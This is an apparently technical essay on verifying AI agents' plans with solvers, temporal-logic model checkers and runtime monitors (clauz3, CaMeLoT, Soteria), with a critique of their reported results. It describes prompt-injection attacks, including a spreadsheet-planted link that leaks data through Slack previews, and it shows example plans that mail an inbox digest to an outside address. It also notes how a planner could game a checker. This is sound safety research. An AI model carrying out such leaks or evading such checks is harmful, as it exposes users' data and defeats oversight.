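With no frame conditions, the rule requires only that foo.txt and bar.txt disappear, and the wildcard call removes both. Meijer adds a frame condition, which he prints only for `delete_file`, and writes that the wildcard plan then fails to verify, but the second row shows that it still passes. A tool's contract is an assumption, and adding an assumption can only rule out cases, so it can never change Z3's result from "unsat" to "sat". The operator has to put a frame condition on the task to reject the wildcard plan. Meijer may have intended this, since he introduces the condition to hold the model to minimal changes. His printed formula also uses an undefined variable `f`, where he presumably meant the old state of the file system.

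A frame condition on the task alone makes the gate too strict. It rejects the wildcard plan but also the correct one, because nothing in the contract prevents `delete_file("foo.txt")` from deleting a.pdf too. The gate accepts the right plan and rejects the wrong one only when both conditions are present. The counterexample is then the one the user would care about, in which notes.txt exists before the plan runs but not after.

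John McCarthy and Patrick Hayes identified this difficulty in 1969 and named it the frame problem. A list of what an action changes doesn't establish what it leaves unchanged. In Brachman and Levesque's (2003) example, a separate axiom has to state that dropping an object doesn't change its colour. Meijer applies the name to the wildcard plan, but it fits the rejected two-call plan better. The wildcard plan passes because the rule omits part of what the user wanted, which is a separate mistake that needs a different correction.

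The program's first call to `s.check()` guards against contradictory assumptions. Suppose an operator wants to protect notes.txt and mistakenly adds an assumption that the file always remains, instead of putting that requirement in the rule. The contract for the wildcard call requires notes.txt to be gone. No case satisfies both, so Z3 would return "unsat" whatever the rule was, and a gate without the first check would accept the plan that deletes the file.

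The program also assumes that the gate knows which files are in the folder. Usually it doesn't, and someone may add a file between the check and the deletion. The gate can instead ask about a single file with an unknown name:

```python
from z3 import *

x = String("x")
exists, remains = Bools("exists remains")
matches = InRe(x, Concat(Full(ReSort(StringSort())), Re(".txt")))

s = Solver()
s.add(Implies(matches, Not(remains)))            # tool's effect
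s.add(Implies(Not(matches), remains == exists))  # tool's frame
s.add(x != "foo.txt", x != "bar.txt")            # a file to leave alone
s.add(remains != exists)                         # that changes anyway
print(s.check())
```

Z3 returns "sat" and can give any name ending in `.txt`, other than the two targets, as an example. Because `x` could be any file, an "unsat" result would have held for every file in every folder.

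### A spending cap in clauz3

In an example from clauz3, a user asks an agent to pay a card bill but to spend no more than $500. The agent writes a program that looks up the balance and pays min(balance, 500). With the minimum written out as a branch, the program and its promises look roughly like this:

```python
@clauz3.guarantee(bank.max_spend(500))
@clauz3.guarantee(bank.only_account("card"))
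def main() -> None:
    owed = balance("card")
    if owed > 500:
        withdraw("card", 500)
    else:
        withdraw("card", owed)
```

clauz3 executes the program symbolically, with an unknown b in place of the balance. At the `if`, it follows both branches and remembers the condition for each. When it reaches a call to a trusted tool, it doesn't run the tool's code. As clauz3's *Generic Effect Specs* explains, it adds the tool's preconditions to the list of things to prove and records the call as an effect fact. Each fact holds the tool's name, the arguments and the condition under which the program reaches the call. This program produces two facts:

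| Tool | Account | Amount | Condition |
|---|---|---|---|
| `withdraw` | card | 500 | b > 500 |
| `withdraw` | card | b | b ≤ 500 |

The promise `max_spend(500)` limits the sum of the amounts, and a fact whose condition is false adds zero to that sum. Z3 therefore has to find a b that satisfies:

```
b >= 0
(500 if b > 500 else 0) + (b if b <= 500 else 0) > 500
```

The first line comes from the contract for `balance`, and the second negates the promise. If b is above 500, the sum is 500. Otherwise the sum is b, which is at most 500. No value of b satisfies both lines, so Z3 returns "unsat" and the cap holds for every possible balance.

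If the agent had written `withdraw("card", owed)` without the branch, Z3 would have found a counterexample, such as a balance of $501. clauz3's *Bank example* includes a test like this and another in which the cap is too tight, presumably because the agent promises a lower limit than its program enforces. clauz3 accepts only literal values such as 500 in a promise, so the agent can't use a calculation to hide a weak promise.

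The line `b >= 0` also matters because `withdraw` requires a non-negative amount. A real card can have a negative balance after an overpayment, and the proof doesn't cover that case. But clauz3 enforces the engineer's conditions while the program runs, so if the balance were −$20, it would stop the program before any money was paid.

Both promises set only upper limits, so a program that does nothing satisfies both, even though the bill goes unpaid. clauz3's vocabulary also allows lower limits on sums and counts, so an engineer could add a promise to pay at least a certain amount. The cap also applies to each program separately, so ten approved programs could spend $5,000 in total.

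### Why a complete list of effects supplies the frame

clauz3 proves the cap without any frame condition. clauz3's documentation contrasts this with Meijer's method. His formulas describe the state of the file system, which a tool might change in any way that no formula excludes. clauz3's formulas describe a complete list of the program's effects, so the prover can conclude that an effect missing from the list doesn't happen.

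An engineer could write the deletion rule in this style:

```python
Delete = effect("delete_file")

@contract
def only_deletes(files: list[str]) -> ContractSpec:
    return Delete.all(lambda d: d.file in files)
```

The wildcard plan produces one fact, in which the file is `*.txt`. The plan fails because `*.txt` isn't in the list `["foo.txt", "bar.txt"]`. The correct plan produces two facts and passes. Neither `notes.txt` nor `a.pdf` appears in any formula.

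The frame condition has become an assumption about the tools. The proof assumes that `delete_file("foo.txt")` does only what its name and argument suggest. If the tool also deletes backups with the same name, that deletion is not among the recorded facts, and the proof still succeeds. The engineer who describes the tools has to check for such effects, along with everything else clauz3 relies on. That includes its modified version of an older prover, the code that turns promises into formulas, and the functions that define the promises, which clauz3 runs as ordinary Python without fully checking them.

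A list of calls also doesn't show what state they leave behind. For this, clauz3 has fluents, which are properties that tools can change, such as whether a door is locked. The engineer gives each tool a successor-state axiom, a formula that derives the property's new value from its old one. For the deletion tool, it would be:

```
remains(f) = exists(f) ∧ ¬(f matches the pattern)
```

This one line is equivalent to the tool's effect and frame conditions together, so nobody can write the effect condition and forget the frame condition. clauz3's home-automation example uses fluents to prove that every door is locked when the program ends.

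### Loops

A loop over three known bills is easy to check, because the prover can copy its body three times. clauz3 does this for loops with a fixed number of passes. When the number of passes is unknown, the prover can check every run up to a chosen bound, which is called bounded model checking. *Practice*, from a 2026 University of Washington course, demonstrates this on a small loop. If the bound is three and a plan exceeds its cap on the fourth bill, the check misses the violation. The gate must also prove that the loop stops within the bound, or have the interpreter stop it there.

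A proof that covers any number of bills needs a loop invariant, a statement that is true before the loop starts and stays true after each pass. For a spending cap, the invariant could be that the total paid so far is at most $500. A loop keeps this true if it pays a bill only when the new total stays within $500. Someone has to find the invariant, and a correct plan still fails the check if the invariant is badly chosen.

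Rules about each item separately are simpler, because the prover can check the loop's body for one arbitrary item. clauz3 supports loops over the rows that a trusted database query returns, and it can prove that a program emails only addresses from a certain column. In one of its examples, a trading program may buy only stocks and quantities that appear in approved orders, but clauz3 doesn't yet require both to come from the same order. If the approved orders are for 10 shares of one company and 1,000 of another, the program could buy 1,000 shares of the first.

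clauz3 doesn't support `while` loops at all. Its test suite includes a harmless program with a bounded `while` loop, whose promise is true, and clauz3 reports a "skip" and refuses to run it. A skip and a failed proof both prevent execution, but only a failed proof comes with a counterexample. The difference is useful to whoever receives the rejection, because a skipped program may only need rewriting. The supported subset is also growing. clauz3's specification of its Python subset still excludes all `for` loops and statements such as `x += 1`, while the newer package handles some of the former and at least the text version of the latter.

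### Text, numbers and solver time

Z3 has had a theory of strings since version 4.5.0, according to its *RELEASE NOTES*, which lets us ask about a file whose name is unknown. The pattern in the formula must match the same file names as the pattern in the tool. In many command shells, `*.txt` skips hidden files, whose names start with a dot, but the regular expression above matches them. When the rule protects hidden files, this mismatch causes only false alarms, because the formula assumes the tool deletes more files than it does. If the tool deleted more than the formula assumed, the gate could accept a plan that deletes the wrong file.

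clauz3 limits its promises about text to a few operations, including comparing the start or end of a string. This is enough for a rule that a program may write only under a certain folder, but the comparison is easy to get wrong. A path that starts with `/work/reports` could lead to `/work/reports-private/`, so the prefix needs a slash at the end. Even then, `/work/reports/../payroll` starts with the right text and leads to another folder. A rule that only compares text needs a precondition that forbids `..` in paths.

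Numbers can also differ between the formula and the program. *Supported Python Subset*, the documentation for another translator from Python to Z3, says that it models Python's floating-point numbers as exact real numbers. In exact arithmetic 0.1 + 0.2 equals 0.3, but Python's result is slightly larger, so a program could exceed a limit that Z3 had proved. Writing amounts as whole cents avoids this. Whole numbers have no maximum size in Python or Z3, but a payment service might store them in 32 bits. A large enough total could then wrap round to a negative number, which the proof wouldn't account for.

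Conditions that begin "for every file" cause a different problem, because Z3 can't try infinitely many names. It uses heuristics to pick instances, and may return "unknown" or run until the time limit. A gate can usually avoid such conditions by listing the known cases or by asking about one arbitrary file, as above. The gate can also give Z3 only some instances of a tool's contract. With fewer assumptions, Z3 considers more cases, so this can cause false alarms but can't hide a violation.

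A short plan can produce a formula that is hard to solve. *Supported Python Subset* warns that multiplying two unknowns, such as a price and a quantity, may be slow. The translation can also make a formula very large. If a program doubles a variable thirty times and the translator substitutes each line into the next, the result contains more than a billion copies of the original variable. Giving each intermediate value its own name keeps the formula to thirty short lines.

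A time limit in seconds makes the verdict depend on how busy the computer is, so the gate might accept a plan on one run and reject the same plan on another. Z3 version 4.5.0 added resource limits to avoid this. They cap the amount of work the solver does, which makes a rejection much easier to reproduce.

### Encoding a written company policy

*Solver-Aided Verification of Policy Compliance in Tool-Augmented LLM Agents* (Winston, Winston and Just, 2026) encodes the tool-use rules from τ²-bench's 1,242-word airline policy. It leaves out rules about the agent's behaviour that aren't tied to a tool. The system is a runtime monitor, but translating the rules would take much the same work for a gate.

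The translation took four attempts. The researchers first asked a language model to write the formulas, but the output was full of syntax errors and undefined symbols. They then gave the model Z3's error messages to fix, and it produced 50 to 60 valid lines that left out many essential rules. Next, Amazon's automated reasoning tool wrote about 600 lines, and another model estimated their coverage at around 95%. But many of the rules were too weak. For example, one allowed customers to cancel within 24 hours of booking but did not forbid cancelling later. In the last attempt, the researchers gave Amazon's tool more precise instructions and corrected the result by hand, partly by running the benchmark to see which rules failed.

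The weak cancellation rule did damage because of how Winston and colleagues question the solver. They ask whether the policy, the known facts and permission for the call can all be true together. "Sat" therefore allows the call and "unsat" blocks it, the reverse of the method described above. Suppose a customer booked three days ago:

```
policy:  booked within 24 hours ⇒ cancellation allowed
fact:    ¬(booked within 24 hours)
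```

Nothing here rules out "cancellation allowed", so Z3 returns "sat" and the call goes through. The usual test is whether permission could be false. It could, so Z3 again returns "sat", but now that result blocks the call. VeriTool, a small open-source checker, uses this convention, so a missing prohibition leads to a false alarm instead of a violation. The researchers' convention, which tests whether permission could be true, has the advantage that a contradictory policy blocks every call instead of allowing every call.

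Before each tool call, GPT-4o reads the conversation and the call's arguments and fills in the facts that the policy depends on. Z3 then checks whether the policy allows the call. If Z3 blocks it, the agent receives the smallest set of conflicting conditions as an explanation and can revise its plan up to three times before returning control to the user. The evaluation used 50 airline tasks with 13 tools and ran each task four times, with GPT-4.1 as both agent and customer.

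About half of the unprotected agent's state-changing calls were invalid. With the solver, the share fell to 29%, though the agent also made fewer correct calls. Overall task success improved only slightly. The agent also became more consistent. When the measure required four successful runs in a row instead of one, its success rate fell by 26%, compared with 40% for the unprotected agent.

An invalid-call rate of 29% may seem high for a system built on a solver, but it could have several causes. The encoding may still have gaps, and GPT-4o may misread the conversation or treat a customer's false claim as true. The benchmark may also count a call as invalid because the task didn't require it, even if no rule forbids it. Z3's reasoning is probably the most reliable part of the system, but its answer depends on formulas and facts that came partly from language models.

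It is also unclear how much a solver adds when it checks one call at a time. When the call is made, the amount, recipient and booking date are usually known, and an ordinary program can compare them with the rule. Yu and colleagues' NOMOS does this on the same airline tasks, deciding in microseconds without a solver or a language model. Its much larger reduction in violations isn't directly comparable, because the agents and the counting differ, but it suggests that a runtime monitor can work without Z3. A solver is more useful in a gate, which must decide before the program has looked up the balance, so its verdict has to hold for every balance.

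### Dafny and Lean

Dafny is a programming language in which contracts are part of the code. Its verifier translates each function and its contract into formulas and normally passes them to Z3, so programmers don't have to write formulas for assignments and branches by hand. They write preconditions, postconditions and loop invariants next to the code instead. Soteria uses Dafny for rules about the order of calls. Using Z3 directly is simpler for a single spending limit, but Dafny is a better choice once plans contain functions or loops of unknown length. The model then has to write the invariants, and the gate will reject a safe plan if the model can't find good ones.

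In Lean, a person or a model writes a proof, and a small program called the kernel checks it. Lean can express statements that are awkward or impossible for an SMT solver, such as a claim about every function that a plan might receive. As in proof-carrying code, a slow proof search delays whoever writes the proof, not the gate. But while Z3 can give notes.txt as a counterexample, a failed attempt at a Lean proof gives none, and the failure may mean that the plan is unsafe or just that the model isn't good enough at proofs.

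*interwhen* (2026) uses Lean before the agent starts work. A language model turns each policy rule into a formal specification, writes a small checking function, and proves that the function matches the specification. The agent can then run the function before each relevant call without waiting for a proof. In one example, the function checks that a refund goes to the right place before the agent cancels an order. As with VeriGuard, if the model misreads a rule, it can end up proving that the function matches a specification that is itself wrong.

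*Lean4Agent* (Wang, Huang and colleagues, 2026) uses Lean to check an agent's whole workflow, a graph of steps that language models carry out. The first of its three layers checks the structure, for instance that no step reads a variable that nothing has set. The second has a language model draft preconditions and postconditions for each step from the step's instructions, then proves that earlier steps establish what later ones need. The third uses Lean, Python programs or another language model to find the step that went wrong in records of actual runs.

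The second layer's proofs rest on an assumption called *LLMExec*, which is that whenever a step's preconditions are true, the language model can produce a result that satisfies the postconditions. This is reasonable for finding badly designed workflows. In one case, the checker caught a step that needed evidence from an earlier step but ran without access to it. But the assumption only guarantees that a good result is possible, while a safety gate has to consider every result the model might produce, including one an attacker has influenced. A workflow can therefore pass Lean4Agent's checks and still leak Michelle's mail.

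The experiments measured usefulness, not safety. Claude Opus 4.6 wrote 40 workflows. For each comparison, the researchers picked three that passed verification and three that failed, and five other models ran them. On 50 hard software bugs from SWE-bench Verified, the models solved 58.3% with the passing workflows and 43.5% with the failing ones. On 100 questions about AI research papers, they answered 36.6% correctly with the passing workflows and 27.5% with the failing ones. Six workflows are a small sample, but every model did better with the passing ones on both benchmarks. Wang and colleagues argue that SMT-based checks don't work well for the more abstract reasoning that Lean allows. That is fair for properties of a whole workflow, such as whether an agent judges several options independently. Checking a spending cap or a list of permitted files doesn't require such abstract reasoning,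 and Z3 has an advantage there because it needs no written proof and can return a counterexample when the plan is wrong.

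## Checking the order of calls across a whole plan

To check some rules, the gate has to examine the sequence of calls on every path through the plan. For example, a company may require approval before every transfer, so whether a transfer is allowed depends on whether the plan obtained approval earlier. A company may also require an agent to close every incident ticket it opens, and a plan breaks that rule if it leaves out the call that closes the ticket.

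### A security automaton for Michelle's mailbox

Schneider (2000), in *Enforceable Security Policies*, introduced security automata for rules about what may follow what. A security automaton reads calls in order and moves between a few states. Meijer suggests one to keep email summaries inside the company. For the rule "no external email after reading the inbox", it needs three states:

```
             fetch_mail             send_email to an outsider
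 NOT READ  -------------->  READ  ---------------------------->  ERROR
```

Any other call leaves the state unchanged, so the agent may still email an outsider before it calls `fetch_mail`.

A runtime monitor tracks the automaton's state through one run, but a gate has to track it along every path through the plan. At an "if", the gate follows both branches, and where they meet it keeps every state that either branch could have reached. It analyzes a loop repeatedly until no new states appear, much as Java's bytecode verifier does with types. The gate rejects the plan if it can reach ERROR on any path.

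This rule catches some leaks that taint analysis misses. One is the plan that sent Eve a fixed lunch message only if Michelle's mail mentioned a merger. The message comes after `fetch_mail`, so the automaton reaches ERROR. The rule also catches the plan that saved the emails as a note and read them back. But it raises more false alarms, because an agent that has read the inbox can't send an outsider even a harmless greeting. The automaton also starts each new plan in NOT READ, so it misses leaks through a note saved by an earlier plan unless the gate keeps the state between plans.

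It can be hard to list all the calls that should lead to ERROR. Invariant Labs' *Agents with Formal Security Guarantees* (2024) describes an agent that reads customer feedback from a spreadsheet and sends a summary to its own user on Slack. Although the message goes only to the user, Slack opens every link in it to show a preview. Text planted in the spreadsheet can make the agent include a link that sends the data to an attacker's server when Slack opens it. Invariant Labs demonstrated this attack on two widely used systems, whose providers have since fixed the flaw. The paper's rule forbids the agent from sending messages with link previews once it has read a spreadsheet or document.

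An automaton with a few fixed states also can't match each approval to its transfer. In *Sapien* (2026), a runtime policy engine, operators describe sequences of calls with regular expressions that can store a value from one call and compare it with a value in a later one.

### Calls that must happen later

A monitor that only watches calls and stops bad ones can enforce only safety properties, a result of Schneider's that Basin et al. (2012) summarize. A rule is a safety property if every violation happens at a definite point and can't be repaired afterwards, as when an agent makes a transfer without approval. Rules that require something to happen eventually, such as closing every open ticket, are called liveness properties. The monitor can't enforce the ticket rule because the agent may still close the ticket later, so there is no call to block.

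A monitor can partly enforce a duty to make a later call by treating "finish" as a call. *MENTOR* (Anand, Chatzi and colleagues, 2026) describes a monitor that blocks the finishing call while a duty is still open and suggests a call that would help to fulfil it. If the duty is to close a ticket, the agent can't declare the task complete while the ticket is open, but the monitor can't make the agent close it. A gate can check the plan before the agent opens the ticket and reject it if it has no closing call.

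Temporal logic can express both kinds of rule. It extends ordinary logic with operators for "always" and "eventually". One version, computation tree logic (CTL), also distinguishes between all paths through a program and some path. The two company rules look like this:

```
AG (transfer → approved)
AG (ticket_opened → AF ticket_closed)
```

A means "on all paths" and E means "on some path". G means "at every step", F "at some step, now or later", X "at the next step" and U "until". The first formula means that on all paths, at every step, if the plan makes a transfer, it already has approval. The second means that on all paths, at every step, if the plan opens a ticket, then on all paths from there the plan eventually closes the ticket. The fact `approved` becomes true when the plan obtains approval and stays true.

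One of CaMeLoT's rules, "confirm the host before isolating it", forbids isolation until the plan has confirmed the host. In CTL, "until" also requires the confirmation to happen, so a plan that finds a false alarm and neither confirms nor isolates anything would break the rule. Anand and colleagues instead use "weak until", which accepts a run in which neither event occurs.

Linear temporal logic (LTL) describes one run at a time and has no operator for "on some path". Dantas and colleagues explain that standard LTL describes infinite runs, and that a variant called LTLf covers plans that end. A program called a model checker determines whether such a formula holds by exploring every reachable state of a finite model. If the formula fails, the checker can usually return a path that breaks it.

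### CaMeLoT

CaMeLoT adds a model checker to CaMeL, a system that fixes a plan before reading any data and applies its policies at runtime. Nikolaou and Eckhoff illustrate CaMeLoT with a request to find Bob's address in a chat channel and tell him about a 3pm meeting.

The planner writes this as restricted Python. CaMeLoT parses the plan into a syntax tree, puts every tool call in a standard form and builds a finite-state model with a state for each call:

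```
START → read channel → extract address → send message → DONE
```

An "if" becomes a fork, and a loop becomes a choice between repeating and exiting. Each state also records which tools the plan has already called.

Next, CaMeLoT labels every value by its origin. From most to least trusted, the labels are literals in the plan, the user's input, results from untrusted tools, and output from the quarantined model. A computed value takes the least trusted label among its inputs. Bob's address comes from the quarantined model, so CaMeLoT marks the message's recipient as tainted. It also marks a value as tainted if it can't determine before the run whether to trust it.

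The model checker nuXmv then tests the formula `AG (call_send_direct_message → recipient_trusted)`. The formula fails at the last call, and nuXmv returns the path that leads there as a counterexample. CaMeLoT turns the counterexample into a written explanation and prompts the planner to repair the plan. It repeats the check until the plan passes or reaches the repair limit. If the plan passes, CaMeL runs it with its usual policies.

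There seems to be no good repair here, because the user asked for an address that appears only in the channel. The planner could pass the check by guessing an address, since literals count as trusted. Repeated repair can make such shortcuts more likely.

CaMeLoT uses ordinary code to turn the plan into a model. *Bridging LLM Planning Agents and Formal Methods* (Ramani, Tawosi and colleagues, 2025) instead uses a language model to translate plans written in English into the finite-state model and the LTL formulas. GPT-5 scored 96.3% on F1, a measure that combines missed cases and false alarms. This approach is useful for reviewing plans, but a gate built this way could approve a mistranslated version of a plan and then let the original run.

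### CaMeLoT's results

Nikolaou and Eckhoff rewrote CaMeL's AgentDojo policies as CTL formulas and could check 22 of the 28 before execution. These include all 11 policies for banking and travel but only 3 of 7 for workplace chat. The remaining policies depend on facts that are known only when the plan runs, such as who can read a file. CaMeLoT leaves almost all confidentiality checks to CaMeL for the same reason.

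They then ran both systems on AgentDojo's 97 tasks without any injected instructions:

| Outcome | Tasks |
|---|---|
| Passes under both systems | 42 |
| Runs under both but does the wrong thing | 22 |
| Blocked by both | 17 |
| Passes only under CaMeLoT | 9 |
| Passes only under CaMeL | 7 |

Every request was harmless, so each blocked plan left a user's task undone. Both systems block 17 of the plans, but CaMeLoT has the advantage of rejecting them before any tool runs.

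In the combined system, a plan has to pass both layers, so about 42 tasks would succeed, compared with 49 under CaMeL alone. CaMeL would still block the nine tasks that pass only under CaMeLoT, mostly because of runtime facts that CaMeLoT doesn't have. The seven tasks that pass only under CaMeL probably fail under CaMeLoT because its labels are cautious. Six of them are office tasks, where CaMeLoT could only partly reproduce CaMeL's labels for 13 of the 14 tools. Repair could recover some of those seven tasks, but the experimenters had switched it off except for unsupported Python operations.

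The second experiment tests rules that CaMeL's checks on single calls can't naturally express. An agent works as a junior analyst in a security operations centre, where it investigates alerts and can isolate a computer (the host) from the network. Nikolaou and Eckhoff wrote one safe plan and seven unsafe variants:

| Rule | What the unsafe plan does |
|---|---|
| Confirm the host before isolating it | Isolates it first |
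| Get approval before a drastic action | Isolates the host without asking |
| Isolation must happen | Never isolates the host |
| Resolve or escalate every ticket | Leaves a ticket open |
| Don't isolate immediately after scanning attachments | Does exactly that |
| Open a ticket before a drastic action | Acts without a ticket |
| Don't block an IP address from an untrusted source | Blocks one supplied by a model |

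CaMeLoT caught all seven, while a simplified CaMeL that just tracked taint caught only the last one. Nikolaou and Eckhoff expected this because they had designed the test around properties that CaMeL lacks. They also had Claude Haiku 4.5 write four bad plans from requests intended to produce them, and CaMeLoT caught all four while CaMeL caught none. These tests show that the formulas work on the chosen mistakes, but they don't measure how often agents make them.

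The approval rule is also weaker than its description. Its formula is satisfied once the plan has called `request_ir_approval`, whether or not the response team agreed. The plan that counts as safe isolates the host on the line after the request without checking the answer, so a refusal would have no effect unless the approval tool itself stops the plan. CaMeLoT also doesn't record the arguments of earlier calls, so approval for one host would count for another. Anand and colleagues avoid this second problem by tracking each case separately. In their travel example, checking the distance from Toronto to Chicago doesn't allow the agent to book a trip from Toronto to Montreal.

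A rule such as "isolation must happen" makes sense for one alert but not for every alert, so CaMeLoT can also derive rules from the user's request. A language model chooses from ten kinds of obligation, such as "b only after a" or "no side effects except these", and ordinary code then checks the tool names and writes the formula. Claude Haiku 4.5 identified exactly the right state-changing tools for 85 of the 97 AgentDojo tasks. In 20 prepared cases, the resulting formulas accepted every correct plan and rejected every bad one.

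Michelle asked only for a summary, so the limit on side effects would make the gate reject a plan with an extra email, even if a poisoned tool description had misled the planner. This works only if the model that derives the rules doesn't read the same description. The gate could also reject a correct plan if the list of allowed tools contains a mistake.

### Loops as free choices

CaMeLoT's model omits the conditions of "if" statements and loops. At each one, nuXmv can take either direction, whatever the data would require. The model therefore contains every path the plan can take, plus some that it can't. One of the extra paths can break a rule:

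```python
for invoice in invoices:
    request_approval(invoice)
for invoice in invoices:
    pay(invoice)
```

Both loops run over the same list, so the plan requests approval for every invoice before it pays any. In the model, however, the first loop can run zero times and the second once. The plan would then pay an invoice without requesting approval, so the gate rejects it even though it is safe. The same happens with two "if" statements that test the same amount.

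Free choices cause more problems for "eventually" rules. Suppose a plan opens a ticket, scans each host on a list and then resolves the ticket. Python leaves the loop when the list ends, but the model includes a path that repeats the loop forever. On that path the ticket stays open, so the second company rule fails. Even `AF done`, which Nikolaou and Eckhoff list as a typical rule, would fail for any plan with such a loop.

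The standard remedy in model checkers is a fairness constraint. *FAIRNESS declarations*, from the manual for nuXmv's predecessor, NuSMV, explains that a path is fair only if the stated condition is true infinitely often. "On all paths" then covers only the fair paths. If the model stays in DONE once it gets there, the condition "the plan is in DONE" excludes every endless loop. It also makes `AF done` true automatically, so the gate needs separate evidence that the loop ends. A Python loop over a finite list provides that evidence if its body doesn't extend the list and every tool call returns. Nikolaou and Eckhoff describe no fairness constraint, and their safe security plan contains no loop, so their results don't show how CaMeLoT handles this case.

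Fairness doesn't help when the required call is inside the loop. If a plan isolates each host on a list, the list might be empty, so the plan might never isolate a host. The gate therefore correctly rejects the plan under the rule "isolation must happen".

For rules about some path, the extra paths cause the opposite error. One request in the CaMeLoT experiments is to check recent transactions and change the password if any look suspicious. The derived formula requires that changing the password remain possible after the check:

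```
AG (get_transactions → EF update_password)
```

A plan could put the password change under a condition that is never true, such as a list having fewer than zero items. The model would still include that branch, so the gate would accept a plan that can never change the password. Treating conditions as free choices therefore errs toward rejecting plans under "all paths" rules, but not under "some path" rules. Nikolaou and Eckhoff remark that linear temporal logic would have been enough for their examples, but it can't express the rule that some path must change the password.

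A contradiction in the model can also make a rule pass whether or not the plan follows it, as contradictory assumptions can with Z3. NuSMV's tutorial gives the example of a state with no successor. So a gate should also check that every plan's model can reach DONE.

### Soteria

Soteria keeps the conditions that CaMeLoT discards. He and colleagues have the planner write a guarded transition system, which is a graph of states connected by steps. Each step makes at most one tool call, and a condition called a guard determines whether the plan may take it. A plan to cancel an airline reservation might be:

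```
LOOKUP       resv = get_reservation(id)      → CHECK_AGE
CHECK_AGE    hrs = hours_since_booking(resv) → CHECK_RULES
CHECK_RULES  if hrs <= 24                    → DO_CANCEL
             if hrs > 24                     → NOT_PERMITTED
DO_CANCEL    cancel_reservation(id)          → DONE
```

Soteria translates the plan into Dafny and checks that every call meets the precondition in the tool's contract, given what the plan has established by then. It also checks progress, meaning that the plan can reach every state and never gets stuck. If the guards were `hrs < 24` and `hrs > 24`, Dafny would report an error because a booking exactly 24 hours old matches neither guard.

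The remaining check is whether the plan obeys the policy. For this, Soteria adds a log that exists only in the proof. It records the step number, arguments and result of each relevant call. At every end state, Dafny must prove from the log that each cancellation follows a check for flown segments on the same reservation, and that the check found none. The plan above never checks for flown segments, so the proof fails and the planner gets the reason.

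Soteria rejects any plan whose graph contains a cycle, so every path ends. Rules that a call must eventually happen therefore need no fairness constraint, and Dafny can check at the end whether the required call is in the log. The planner can combine short, verified sub-plans for standard procedures, using only their contracts, instead of writing long plans. With sub-plans, 65 of 68 airline plans passed verification within the retry limit, compared with 38 of 60 without them.

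In Soteria, unlike in Meijer's pattern, a language model carries out the task with the plan as a guide and may deviate from it. If full verification fails, Soteria continues with the best partly verified plan. A runtime monitor checks each call against the same contracts and policy rules and blocks violations, so the rules still apply when the agent leaves the plan. For the customer-service tasks, Soteria writes a new plan at each turn of the conversation, so it isn't designed to keep untrusted data away from the planner.

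### Soteria's results

He and colleagues tested Soteria with four models on 207 tasks: 50 airline tasks, 114 retail tasks and 43 from Toolathlon, a benchmark of long office and computer tasks. Conformance, the share of tasks without a rule violation, was 100% with Soteria for every model and benchmark, and at most 93% with the baselines. Soteria's success rate, the share of tasks completed without a violation, was 4.7 to 43.9 percentage points above the best baseline for each model and benchmark.

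The scoring appears to use the same rules as the monitor, because He and colleagues describe only one set of 98 formulas and count violations against it. The monitor blocks calls that would break those formulas, so a score of 100% is almost guaranteed. That score is evidence that the monitor works, but not that the agents followed the written policies.

The formulas don't cover everything in those policies. The airline offers $100 per passenger for a cancelled flight and $50 for a delayed one, but the formula accepts either amount in either case. None of the 24 airline formulas requires the customer's confirmation before a change, a rule that unprotected agents often broke in the NOMOS study. He and colleagues also corrected some formulas and added others while auditing their results, so the tasks aren't an independent test of the final rules.

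The success rates partly reflect the same scoring. On Toolathlon, unguarded Claude Opus 4.6 completed 30.2% of tasks, but only 11.6% without a violation, often because it didn't read a file before or after writing it. Soteria completed 18.6%, all without violations, so its success rate was higher but its completion rate was lower. But on the airline and retail tasks, Soteria completed at least as many tasks as every baseline with all four models. The largest gain was for Opus in retail, where completion rose from 53.5% to 90.4%. Without a plan, Opus often gathered all the information it needed and then transferred the customer to a human instead of making the change.

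An ablation on the 50 airline tasks adds Soteria's parts one at a time:

| Configuration | GPT-5.4-mini: success | GPT-5.4-mini: conformance | Gemini 3 Flash: success | Gemini 3 Flash: conformance |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Unverified plan | 44% | 74% | 32% | 54% |
| With verification | 46% | 80% | 32% | 56% |
| With sub-plans | 50% | 80% | 38% | 58% |
| With runtime monitor | 60% | 100% | 62% | 100% |

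Verification alone gained one task for GPT-5.4-mini and none for Gemini. The monitor made the largest difference, and Gemini's entire gain came from fewer violations, since completion stayed at 62%. The ablation doesn't include the monitor without a verified plan, so we can't tell how much verification contributes once the monitor is on.

The closest comparison is AgentSpec, another runtime monitor, but one that doesn't use a plan. Over five runs of the airline tasks with GPT-5.4-mini, Soteria's average success rate was 50.8% and AgentSpec's was 48.0%, with overlapping confidence intervals. Soteria had only three planning retries in these runs, compared with eight in the main experiment. Planning also adds to Soteria's cost, which was 1.7 to 6.7 times that of an unguarded agent on the airline and retail tasks. On Toolathlon, which needs only one plan per task, Soteria was cheaper than the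 unguarded agent with every model.

Soteria also has a strict mode that accepts only fully verified plans and allows only the calls the plan permits at each state. This mode needs no separate policy monitor and is much closer to Meijer's "generate, verify, execute", but He and colleagues report no success rates for it.

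## Checking code as the model writes it and repairing what is rejected

A checker that runs while the model is still writing a plan can catch a mistake after a single line, or even part of a word, but only if nothing later in the plan can undo the mistake.

### What an unfinished plan already decides

Suppose a company has two rules. Mailbox contents must not leave the company, and a plan that makes a payment must ask a manager to approve it before the plan ends. A model writes this plan line by line:

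```
1  emails = fetch_mail()
2  pay(to="Acme", amount=120)
3  digest = summarize_emails(emails)
4  send_email(to="eve@example.org", body=digest)
5  request_approval(payee="Acme", amount=120)
```

| After line | Mailbox rule | Approval rule |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Not broken yet | Nothing to approve |
| 2 | Not broken yet | Approval still needed |
| 3 | Not broken yet | Approval still needed |
| 4 | Broken, whatever follows | Approval still needed |
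| 5 | Broken | Met |

After line 4, every possible completion contains the leak, so a checker can stop the model there. It should not stop the model early for the missing approval, because the model can still add it. The plan would break the approval rule only if it ended without line 5. If the company required approval before the payment, line 2 would break the rule immediately.

Checking an unfinished plan can therefore reject it early but can't accept it, because a later line could add a leak. A forbidden call also rules out only the completions in which that call can run. If line 4 were inside a function, the plan would leak nothing until another line called that function.

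The same uncertainty exists within a line. After `send_email(to="eve`, the address could still be a colleague's. After `to="eve@example.org", body=`, the message could still be a fixed greeting. *Projectional Decoding* (2026) makes the general point that a checker for unfinished work has to represent what is still unknown.

### Limiting what the model can write next

A language model writes one token (a word or part of a word) at a time. At each step it gives every token in its vocabulary a probability, and the software running the model picks one. In constrained decoding, a separate program sets the probability of every unacceptable token to zero before the software picks, as *Mitigating Errors in LLM-Generated Web API Invocations via Retrieval-Augmented Generation* (2026) explains.

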